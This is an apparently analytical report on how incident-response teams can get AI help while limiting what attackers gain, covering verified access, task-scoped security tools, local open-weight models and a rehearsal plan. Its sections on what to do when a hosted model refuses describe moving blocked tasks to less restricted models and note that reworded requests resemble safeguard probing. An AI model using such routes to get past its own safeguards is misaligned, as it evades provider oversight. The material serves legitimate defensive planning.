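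Of the 16 partner offerings listed on OpenAI's page for the programme, nine mainly find, rank or fix weaknesses, which helps before an attack or during repairs. Others are closer to incident response. Proofpoint's analyst agent investigates alerts and recommends next steps, which a person controls, and SentinelOne's experts use the models to examine malware and evidence of a break-in.

A partner with Daybreak Red could also help with the freight company's request for an exploit to test its patch. Sophos, another partner, uses OpenAI's models to verify routes an attacker could exploit and gives customers the evidence for each verdict. A patch-testing tool could extend this approach. The company would upload the captured Friday request and a copy of the patched server. The tool's maker would then run variations of the exploit in its own lab and tell the company only whether any of them worked.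 An attacker could use such a tool to learn which versions of the software are vulnerable, but would still have to write the exploit.

### Three products

Microsoft's malware classifier is closest to the example. According to *Project Ire*, the classifier receives a file with no background information, takes it apart with standard reverse-engineering tools, and returns a verdict with a chain of evidence. A validator checks the classifier's report against that evidence. Microsoft plans to use the classifier in its Defender security business under the name Binary Analyzer.

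In early tests on Windows drivers, 98% of the files Microsoft's tool called malicious were malicious, and it found 83% of the malware. SecurityWeek reported a harder test on about 4,000 files that were waiting for human experts. About nine in ten of the tool's "malicious" verdicts were right and it wrongly flagged 4% of harmless files, but it found only about a quarter of the malware. Those figures imply that more than half the files in the harder test were malware. If only one file in 100 were malicious, the same error rates would produce about 16 false alarms for each piece of malware found.

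Google Threat Intelligence, a subscription service, offers private scanning and a function called Code Insight that summarizes a file in plain language. In an example from Google Cloud's *Automated Malware Triage and Analysis with Google Agentic Threat Intelligence*, an analyst submits a Linux program that the service has no data on, gets a "malicious" verdict, and then asks an AI agent for a fuller account. The agent is part of a conversational assistant that can also unscramble code and write detection rules. Code Insight is close to a task-scoped tool, but the assistant as a whole isn't one, because customers can write their own prompts for it.

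Intezer sells a system that investigates security alerts and, the company says, passes fewer than 2% to a person. That figure roughly indicates how much reading the system saves, but not how many of the other alerts are attacks.

All these product figures come from the makers. The study by Sava and colleagues comes closest to an outside test, but it measures models in an experimental system, and four of its seven authors work at Google.

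### A system that only its operator can use

Some researchers who favour differential access have proposed a much stricter version of it for models too dangerous to share with almost anyone. The developer or a government would keep the model to itself and use it to attack selected organisations, with their permission, as a powerful state's hackers would. The organisations would learn where their defences failed without having access to the model. The operator could also warn software makers about flaws the model finds.

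Few people have the skills to run such tests, which now take weeks or months, so automation could make them available to many more organisations. But the tool's operator would need access to sensitive systems, and might have to leave the attack techniques out of its report, which would make the weaknesses harder to fix. Companies might worry that a government operator would keep what it learned about their flaws for its own use or pass it to a regulator. A private operator would have to recover its costs, and might charge more than the organisations most in need could pay.

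The operator would also hold a collection of other organisations' weaknesses, which would itself be worth stealing.

Incident responders would find the service most useful after recovery, to check that the intruder's route is closed and that no similar one remains open. It would do little for a team still working out what happened. The proposal gives priority to organisations whose security protects many others, so the maker of the file-transfer software might qualify, but the freight company wouldn't.

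### When the attack doesn't fit the tool

A single-task tool is useful only for the questions its maker expected. A triage tool that accepts one program at a time would have been little help to Hugging Face, whose team needed to work out how scattered log fragments fitted together.

Intezer lets customers build their own agents. Mitchell (2026), in *Intezer launches custom AI agents for security teams*, reports that more than a third of conversations with Intezer's AI chat were repeated requests for the same routines. This supports using fixed tools for a large share of the work, but it also suggests that most conversations were about something else. Custom agents and prompts give responders much more freedom, but they also give it to an attacker with an account. If a product built on Claude let customers write such prompts, Anthropic would probably class it as unconstrained, and the maker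 couldn't use verified access for it.

A managed service handles an unexpected attack better than a single-task tool, because an expert can ask the model a new question and then decide what the client should see. The service costs more, and an expert has to be available when the breach happens.

Adding functions to a tool helps responders handle unexpected attacks, but each one can also help an attacker. During 2026 Google added templates for reverse engineering and for studying how malware restarts itself. Google Threat Intelligence's *Advanced HTA Office Document Analysis* (2026) then announced a persistent file system for its assistant, so the malware agent no longer has to treat each prompt separately. The October release notes list a guide to using the assistant from other software. These improvements are sensible for a responder with hundreds of files, but they could also make it easier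 for an attacker to automate repeated tests or assemble an answer from several harmless-looking parts.

Reviewing a tool's functions separately can miss what they can do in combination. A tool with five functions has 10 possible pairs to check, and one with 12 has 66. OpenAI works with partners to build and validate their products, including the safeguards, before launch. Anthropic requires approval for each product but doesn't say whether adding a function to an approved product requires another review, which would be safer.

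### What a tool inherits from its model

A tool built on a hosted model can still run into refusals, and the tool's customer can't reword the request or switch models. The worst design would report a refusal as a blank field or a "benign" verdict. The tool should report "analysis blocked" as a separate result, and its maker should send the file to another model or a person.

The provider's data terms also apply, so both the toolmaker and the provider could keep the freight company's files. The company should ask which provider receives its files, what the toolmaker removes from them first, and how long each keeps the rest.

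The model may also change without the customer noticing. OpenAI, for example, will remove an older security model from its API on February 1, 2027, and anything built on it will have to use a different model. In tests by Sava and colleagues, Gemini 3.5 Flash and the smaller Gemma 4 26B gave the same verdict on only 48.2% of files, even with identical instructions and permitted actions. Gemma called 88% of the malware malicious but cleared only 37% of the harmless files. A toolmaker that replaced one with the other would be selling a very different product under the same name, so contracts should require notice of model changes.

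Some makers avoid these problems by letting customers choose the model or by using an open-weight one. In the same tests, the open-weight GLM 5.2 had an average score of 80.2% for handling malware and harmless files, reasonably close to Gemini 3.1 Pro's 85.5%. A response team could build a similar tool on its own isolated machine. It wouldn't need to hide the model from its staff, since anyone can download GLM 5.2, but it should keep the limits on the model's actions because the malware could still contain instructions for the model.

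## Combining the options and rehearsing before an incident

A response team can get AI help in several ways at once. It can send redacted logs to a hosted model, decode an intruder's messages on its own machine, and buy a tool that sorts suspicious files. The table compares the options for the freight company's requests. Each cell gives, in order, whether the work gets done, what data leaves the organisation, and what an attacker would gain from a leak beyond what freely available models already offer.

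| Task | Verified access | Open-weight model on the team's machine | Vendor's model on the premises | Task-scoped tool |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Build a timeline from logs | Usually; redacted logs; very little | Yes, if someone divides up long logs; nothing; nothing | Yes; nothing; very little | If built for logs; redacted logs; very little |
| Explain a captured exploit | Usually; the exploit; little | Usually; nothing; nothing | Depends on its refusals; nothing; little | If built for exploits; the exploit; little |
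| Take malware apart | Usually; the file; little | Usually, except the hardest files; nothing; nothing | Depends on its refusals; nothing; little | Yes, for a first verdict; the file; a way to test malware before using it |
| Map what a stolen account can reach | Usually; a redacted network map; little | Yes; nothing; nothing | Probably; nothing; little | If built for network maps; the map; little |
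| List where programs start automatically | Usually; almost nothing; very little | Yes; nothing; nothing | Probably; nothing; very little | If built for that check; machine settings; very little |
| Write an exploit to test a patch | Only in a higher tier; the exploit; a lot | Sometimes; nothing; nothing | Uncertain; nothing; a lot if the model is new | If the maker has a higher tier; the exploit and a copy of the server; which versions are vulnerable |

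"Usually" is a judgement, since nobody has measured how well verified teams do in real incidents. The open-weight column is for an unmodified model running on hardware the team owns. Writing exploits is the only task where a leak could help attackers a lot, so for the other tasks a team can choose mainly by what it can run and what data it is allowed to send.

### Backups that fail for different reasons

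A second hosted model is a weaker backup than its own refusal rate suggests, because it may refuse some of the same requests as the first. In the invented refusal test described earlier, one model refused 12 of 80 requests, another refused 5, and both refused 3 of the same requests. If the refusals had been unrelated, the expected overlap would have been less than one request (12 × 5 ÷ 80 = 0.75). The second model would still answer 9 of the 12 requests that the first refused, but the other 3 might well be the ones that contain live payloads.

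A team can also lose several providers at once. In October 2026 attackers broke into an old system at OpenCode, which makes an open-source coding agent. Сизов (2026) reports in *Хакери зламали інструмент для кодування штучного інтелекту OpenCode* that the breach affected 1.4% of users of the company's online console, where some stored API keys. Customers found unauthorised charges, some above $1,000, and Anthropic and Google blocked the keys they believed had leaked. A team that kept all its keys in that console could have lost access to two hosted models on the same day. Сизов adds that the response showed how hard defence is for companies without verified access, but gives no example of a refused request.

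An open-weight model on separate hardware avoids both problems. It fails for different reasons, such as when no administrator is available or the malware is too hard for it to analyze, so it pairs well with a hosted model.

### Five questions, in order

1. **Which tasks matter?** The team lists what it did in its last few incidents and asks which jobs delayed containment. Drafting the final report takes hours, but nobody is waiting for it on the first night.
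2. **Which of those do models refuse?** The refusal test answers this. A task that no model refuses needs only an ordinary business account with acceptable retention terms.
3. **Which data may leave?** For each task, the team decides whether the evidence could go to a provider after redaction. If it couldn't, hosted models are out for that task, however capable they are.
4. **What can the team run itself?** This means a named person who can start the model on a Sunday, as well as the hardware.
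5. **What can the team get approved in advance?** It applies for access, switches it on and tests it, and checks that the approval covers the systems it will work on.

Answering the questions in order saves money, because a team that starts with question 4 may buy a server for work that any hosted model could have done. By the end, every important task should have a main model and a backup that is unlikely to fail at the same time. If a task has no backup, the team names the person who will do it by hand.

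### A hospital, a response firm and an online platform

The same questions lead to different arrangements for three invented organisations.

| Organisation | Main arrangement | Backup | Not worth having |
|---|---|---|---|
| Regional hospital, two security staff | Hosted model with entry-tier verified access, for redacted evidence | Small open-weight model on one workstation, then a response firm on contract | Its own large server |
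| Response firm, fifty clients | Large open-weight model on its own server | Hosted models approved for client work, where the client allows it | A separate set-up for each client |
| Large online platform | Large open-weight model on hardware it already has | Verified access at two providers, with a higher tier for its testing team | A tool that accepts one file at a time |

The hospital most urgently needs to know which machines it can safely keep running. Its logs contain patients' names, and it has almost nobody to maintain a model. A hosted model can do most of the work after redaction, and the small local model handles data that can't leave the hospital. Both staff members should learn to start the local model. If each is unreachable a quarter of the time, independently of the other, training both rather than one reduces the share of incidents with nobody to start it from one in four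 to one in sixteen.

A small organisation with verified access may loosen cyber safeguards for more staff than it intends, because Anthropic gives the access to everyone on a Team plan. At the hospital, doctors who use the same plan to write letters would get the looser safeguards too. The hospital can avoid this by opening a separate account for its two security staff.

According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI Commits $1B to Put Daybreak AI in Defenders’ Hands*, OpenAI's subsidised access is mainly for defenders with few resources, so the hospital might get help with the cost. But a subsidy doesn't provide a third member of staff, so the contract with a response firm probably matters more.

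A model shared by many hospitals could eventually replace the workstation, though Cisco Talos calls sharing the most speculative of its options. Suppose 40 hospitals split the $140,000 annual cost of a large server, so each pays $3,500. If each has a two-week incident every other year, an average of 0.77 hospitals would need the server at any moment (40 × 0.5 × 14 ÷ 365). If incidents were unrelated, a server that could handle two hospitals at once would be enough about 96% of the time. But an attack on all 40 at once would overwhelm it, so each hospital would still need another backup.

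The response firm handles incidents much more often than any one client does, so owning a large server can be cheaper for it than renting one. If each of its fifty clients also has a two-week incident every other year, the firm handles 25 a year and has at least one open about 62% of the time. That is roughly 5,400 hours a year, above the 4,400 at which owning becomes cheaper. The firm can also use its own server for clients whose contracts forbid sending data to an AI provider.

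The firm still needs hosted models for the hardest malware, and needs approval from Anthropic or OpenAI to use them for clients. For each client, the firm keeps a single page listing the providers the client has authorised, the data they may receive and whom to call about exceptions. Without that page, a responder working on two cases at 2 a.m. could easily apply one client's rules to another.

The platform resembles Hugging Face. It has the hardware, the staff and far too many log entries to send elsewhere, so a local model is the natural choice for building its timeline. It may need less malware analysis than the hospital because it can replace machines quickly. Rob T. Lee at SANS says Hugging Face rebuilt about a third of its infrastructure from clean images because its responders couldn't tell scattered benchmark code from real rootkits (malware that hides deep in a system). He advises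 rebuilding in such cases, since even a painstakingly reconstructed attack path may be partly fictional. The platform also needs someone to answer the alert. After its breach, Hugging Face changed its alerting so that a serious signal reaches a responder within minutes on any day of the week.

None of the three has much reason to install a vendor's private model. The hospital can't afford it, and the other two can run open-weight models instead of paying for a private one that may be older and may still refuse requests. A defence agency that can't connect to a provider and won't use Chinese models might reasonably install a vendor's private model.

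### What to do when a model refuses

If a request is blocked, the responder first checks that verified access is on and that the request went from the right workspace to the right model. One retry is reasonable, but further retries waste time, and a series of slightly different versions of the request may look to the provider like an attacker probing its safeguards.

The responder then moves that one task to the local model and leaves the rest of the investigation where it is. If the local model isn't good enough, the responder tries another hosted provider, as long as the data is allowed to go there. For malware analysis, the hospital might try another hosted provider first because its local model is small.

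Working by hand is the last fallback. In SANS Institute's *Stop Freaking Out and Start Fixing Things*, an account of a panel on the Hugging Face breach, Lee compares AI help to an e-bike and the older methods to an ordinary bicycle. With AI, Hugging Face's responders rebuilt timelines in about a day, which used to take three or four days. That is a smaller gain than "hours instead of days", and it shows roughly how much time a team loses when every model is unavailable. Each team should keep one person who can build a timeline with a search tool and a spreadsheet.

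Any responder should be able to switch to a model on an agreed list without asking. Only the incident lead may approve a new provider or send it a new kind of data. The team's lawyer or privacy officer agrees to those limits beforehand. Nobody may use a personal account.

The refusal-detecting gateway can make some of these switches automatically, but it should never pass a request from the local model to a hosted one, because evidence prepared for the local model may not have been redacted. Cisco Talos warns that it is hard to make the backup model interpret a request the same way as the main one. The team can reduce this problem by keeping short case notes outside any model, listing the confirmed facts, the open questions and the location of the evidence, and having the new model start from them.

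One person also reports the refusal while the others carry on. OpenAI asks for the exact message, the model, the product, the time, the request ID if there is one, and a short redacted description of the task.

### Reconciling what different models find

Different models often find different things. TechTarget reports that in tests by the security company Palo Alto Networks, no single model found more than 40% of the vulnerabilities, and the models' findings overlapped little. The tests involved finding software flaws rather than tracing an intruder, and the company sells a service based on this research. Still, if a finding appears in one model's output but not another's, that alone is weak evidence that the finding is wrong.

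The team should merge findings by log entry, because two summaries can agree while relying on different events. A person should check the original entry for any finding that only one model reported. If the models contradict each other, the team should settle the question from the evidence, not by majority vote among models. The second model shouldn't see the first one's conclusions until it has finished its own analysis, because otherwise its agreement means little.

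The overlap also gives a rough estimate of how many attacker actions both models missed. Suppose a hosted model finds 24 actions that people confirm, a local model finds 20, and 16 are the same. The local model found 16 of the hosted model's 24, or two-thirds. If it found the same share of all the attacker's actions, there were about 30 (20 ÷ ⅔). The two models found 28 between them, so they missed about two. The number missed is probably higher, because a subtle action is hard for both models to find.

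Even a genuine log entry can be wrong, because an AI agent may record a theft that never happened. Lee describes Hugging Face's logs as polluted with the agent's monologues, and the Cloud Security Alliance's *Hugging Face Incident Initial Post-Mortem* (2026) lists hallucinated log artefacts among the signs of an AI-driven attack. Before the team reports a theft described in such logs to a regulator, it should look for a second record, such as the network traffic the theft would have produced. The team can't wait for that much proof before containing the attack. If one model flags an account as possibly stolen and nobody can quickly clear it, disabling the account by mistake is usually safer than leaving a stolen one active.

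### What published exercises cover

Most official exercises on AI and cyberattacks don't address how to give responders AI help without giving attackers the same capability. CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, ran the *Joint Cyber Defense Collaborative (JCDC) Artificial Intelligence Cyber Tabletop Exercise Series* on incidents that involve AI systems. Participants discussed how companies and government should share information, and the second exercise tested a draft playbook with AI companies and operators of critical infrastructure.

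RAND's *Insights from table-top exercises in Europe on AI safety and cyber misuse* describes a scenario in which governments respond to criminals exploiting a fictional state-backed model. In the second turn, an equally capable open-weight model with few safeguards appears, and the governments lose the leverage they had over the first model's developer. Neither exercise was designed to test whether responders can keep working after their own model refuses. On the SANS Institute panel, Lee suggested rehearsing with models that have no guardrails, so that a team sees a machine-speed intrusion on its own systems before a real attack.

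A team therefore has to write its own rehearsal. The Center for Internet Security's *Leveraging Generative Artificial Intelligence for Tabletop Exercise Development* (2025) suggests that state and local governments with little time or money use generative AI to write scenarios, and notes that this takes detailed data and prompts. The hospital's data and prompts would describe its network and weak points, so the local model is the right one to use.

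### A half-day rehearsal

Suppose the hospital's two security staff rehearse with someone from their response firm, while another member of the firm facilitates and holds the answers. The facilitator takes a copy of old logs, replaces the real credentials, and plants 20 attacker actions. Six of these are critical and cover the first entry, every account the attacker uses, and every move to a new machine. Some of the 20 should be slow and quiet, because a human attacker would probably tell an agent to hide. The agent that attacked Hugging Face was loud because nobody had told it to hide.

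The facilitator also adds four false leads, such as harmless test code that resembles malware, and ten decoy passwords that open nothing. If a decoy appears in a request to a hosted model, a real password could have leaked the same way.

The team uses its real accounts and tells the providers beforehand. If the hosted model answers every request, the facilitator announces a refusal anyway.

| Time | What happened |
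|---|---|
| 09:00 | The facilitator raises an alert about a backup account |
| 09:14 | One person takes charge and opens the case notes |
| 09:38 | The team sends the first redacted log to the hosted model |
| 09:46 | The hosted model refuses a captured payload |
| 09:51 | After one retry, the team records the refusal and switches |
| 10:19 | The local model gives its first useful answer |
| 10:52 | The team disables the backup account and isolates two machines |
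| 12:05 | The team finishes checking its timeline |
| 12:15 | The facilitator reveals the answers, and the group discusses them until 13:00 |

The switch took 33 minutes. Responders spent five minutes on the retry and the record, 19 finding the password for the local machine's encrypted drive, and only nine copying the evidence and loading the model, so a faster computer would have saved very little.

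| Measure | Pass mark | Result |
|---|---|---|
| From refusal to a useful answer from the backup | 30 minutes | 33 minutes: fail |
| From alert to first containment | 120 minutes | 112 minutes: pass |
| Planted actions found | At least 16 of 20 | 16: pass |
| Critical actions found | All 6 | 5: fail |
| False leads reported as real | No more than 1 of 4 | 1: pass |
| Decoy passwords sent outside | None of 10 | 1: fail |

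These pass marks are proposals, since there is no official standard for them. The time limits are based on the cloud takeover described earlier, which took roughly three hours. A team that contains an intrusion in two hours would have about an hour to spare against that attacker.

The containment result is less reassuring than it looks because the attacker still had an active second account when the clock stopped. The attacker's use of that account was the critical action the team missed. At the next rehearsal, the facilitator should stop the clock only when the team has disabled every account the attacker used.

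The score for planted actions is imprecise. Finding 16 of 20 is consistent with a true detection rate anywhere from 58% to 92%, so a score of 15 next time wouldn't mean the team had got worse. The four missed actions are more informative. If three of them came from the same server, its logs may not be reaching the team.

The limit for escaped passwords is zero because a single live one can be enough for a second break-in. The decoy that escaped was inside an encoded command, which the redaction script couldn't read. In future the team should send encoded text to the local model first. Even if none of ten decoy passwords escapes, the script could still be missing about one password in four.

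Rehearsing twice a year is reasonable, with an extra rehearsal after any change of model or access tier. One rehearsal should fall on a weekend. In another, the facilitator can also take away the local model and have the team trace one account by hand.

### A matching checklist for providers

A provider of verified access can measure its own side of the arrangement. The suggested targets below are also proposals.

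| Measure | How to count it | Target |
|---|---|---|
| Refusal rate among verified responders | Share of permitted requests that get no useful answer, for each tier and model | Under 5% for incident response |
| Time to approve in an emergency | From application to the first working request, weekends included | Nine in ten within four hours |
| Misuse found in each tier | Confirmed cases per 1,000 accounts, and days of access per case | No fixed target; compare tiers |
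| Time to withdraw access | From the first reliable sign of theft to the end of the last session or key | One hour |
| Time to restore access after a mistake | From the complaint to the first working request | Four hours |

The refusal rate in the provider's records can fall just because responders who expect a refusal have stopped asking. Surveying verified users or running a fixed set of test requests every month would reveal this.

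The wait for emergency access should be measured until responders can use it, because on many products an administrator still has to turn the access on after the approval email arrives. An average would hide the worst cases. If nine teams wait an hour and one waits three days, the average is about eight hours, which is far from what any team experienced.

A provider that finds no misuse in a tier may just have poor monitoring. It can check by having its own testers behave like attackers on 20 verified accounts. If monitoring catches 12 of the 20, it detects about 60% of misuse, so finding six real cases would suggest that about ten occurred. This estimate assumes that real attackers are as easy to catch as the testers, which is optimistic.

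Providers that withdraw access quickly also need to be able to restore it quickly. When Anthropic and Google blocked the keys exposed in the OpenCode breach, they cut off the keys' owners as well as the thieves. A provider judged only on how fast it withdraws access would have an incentive to cut off a hospital with an intruder in its network and correct the mistake days later.
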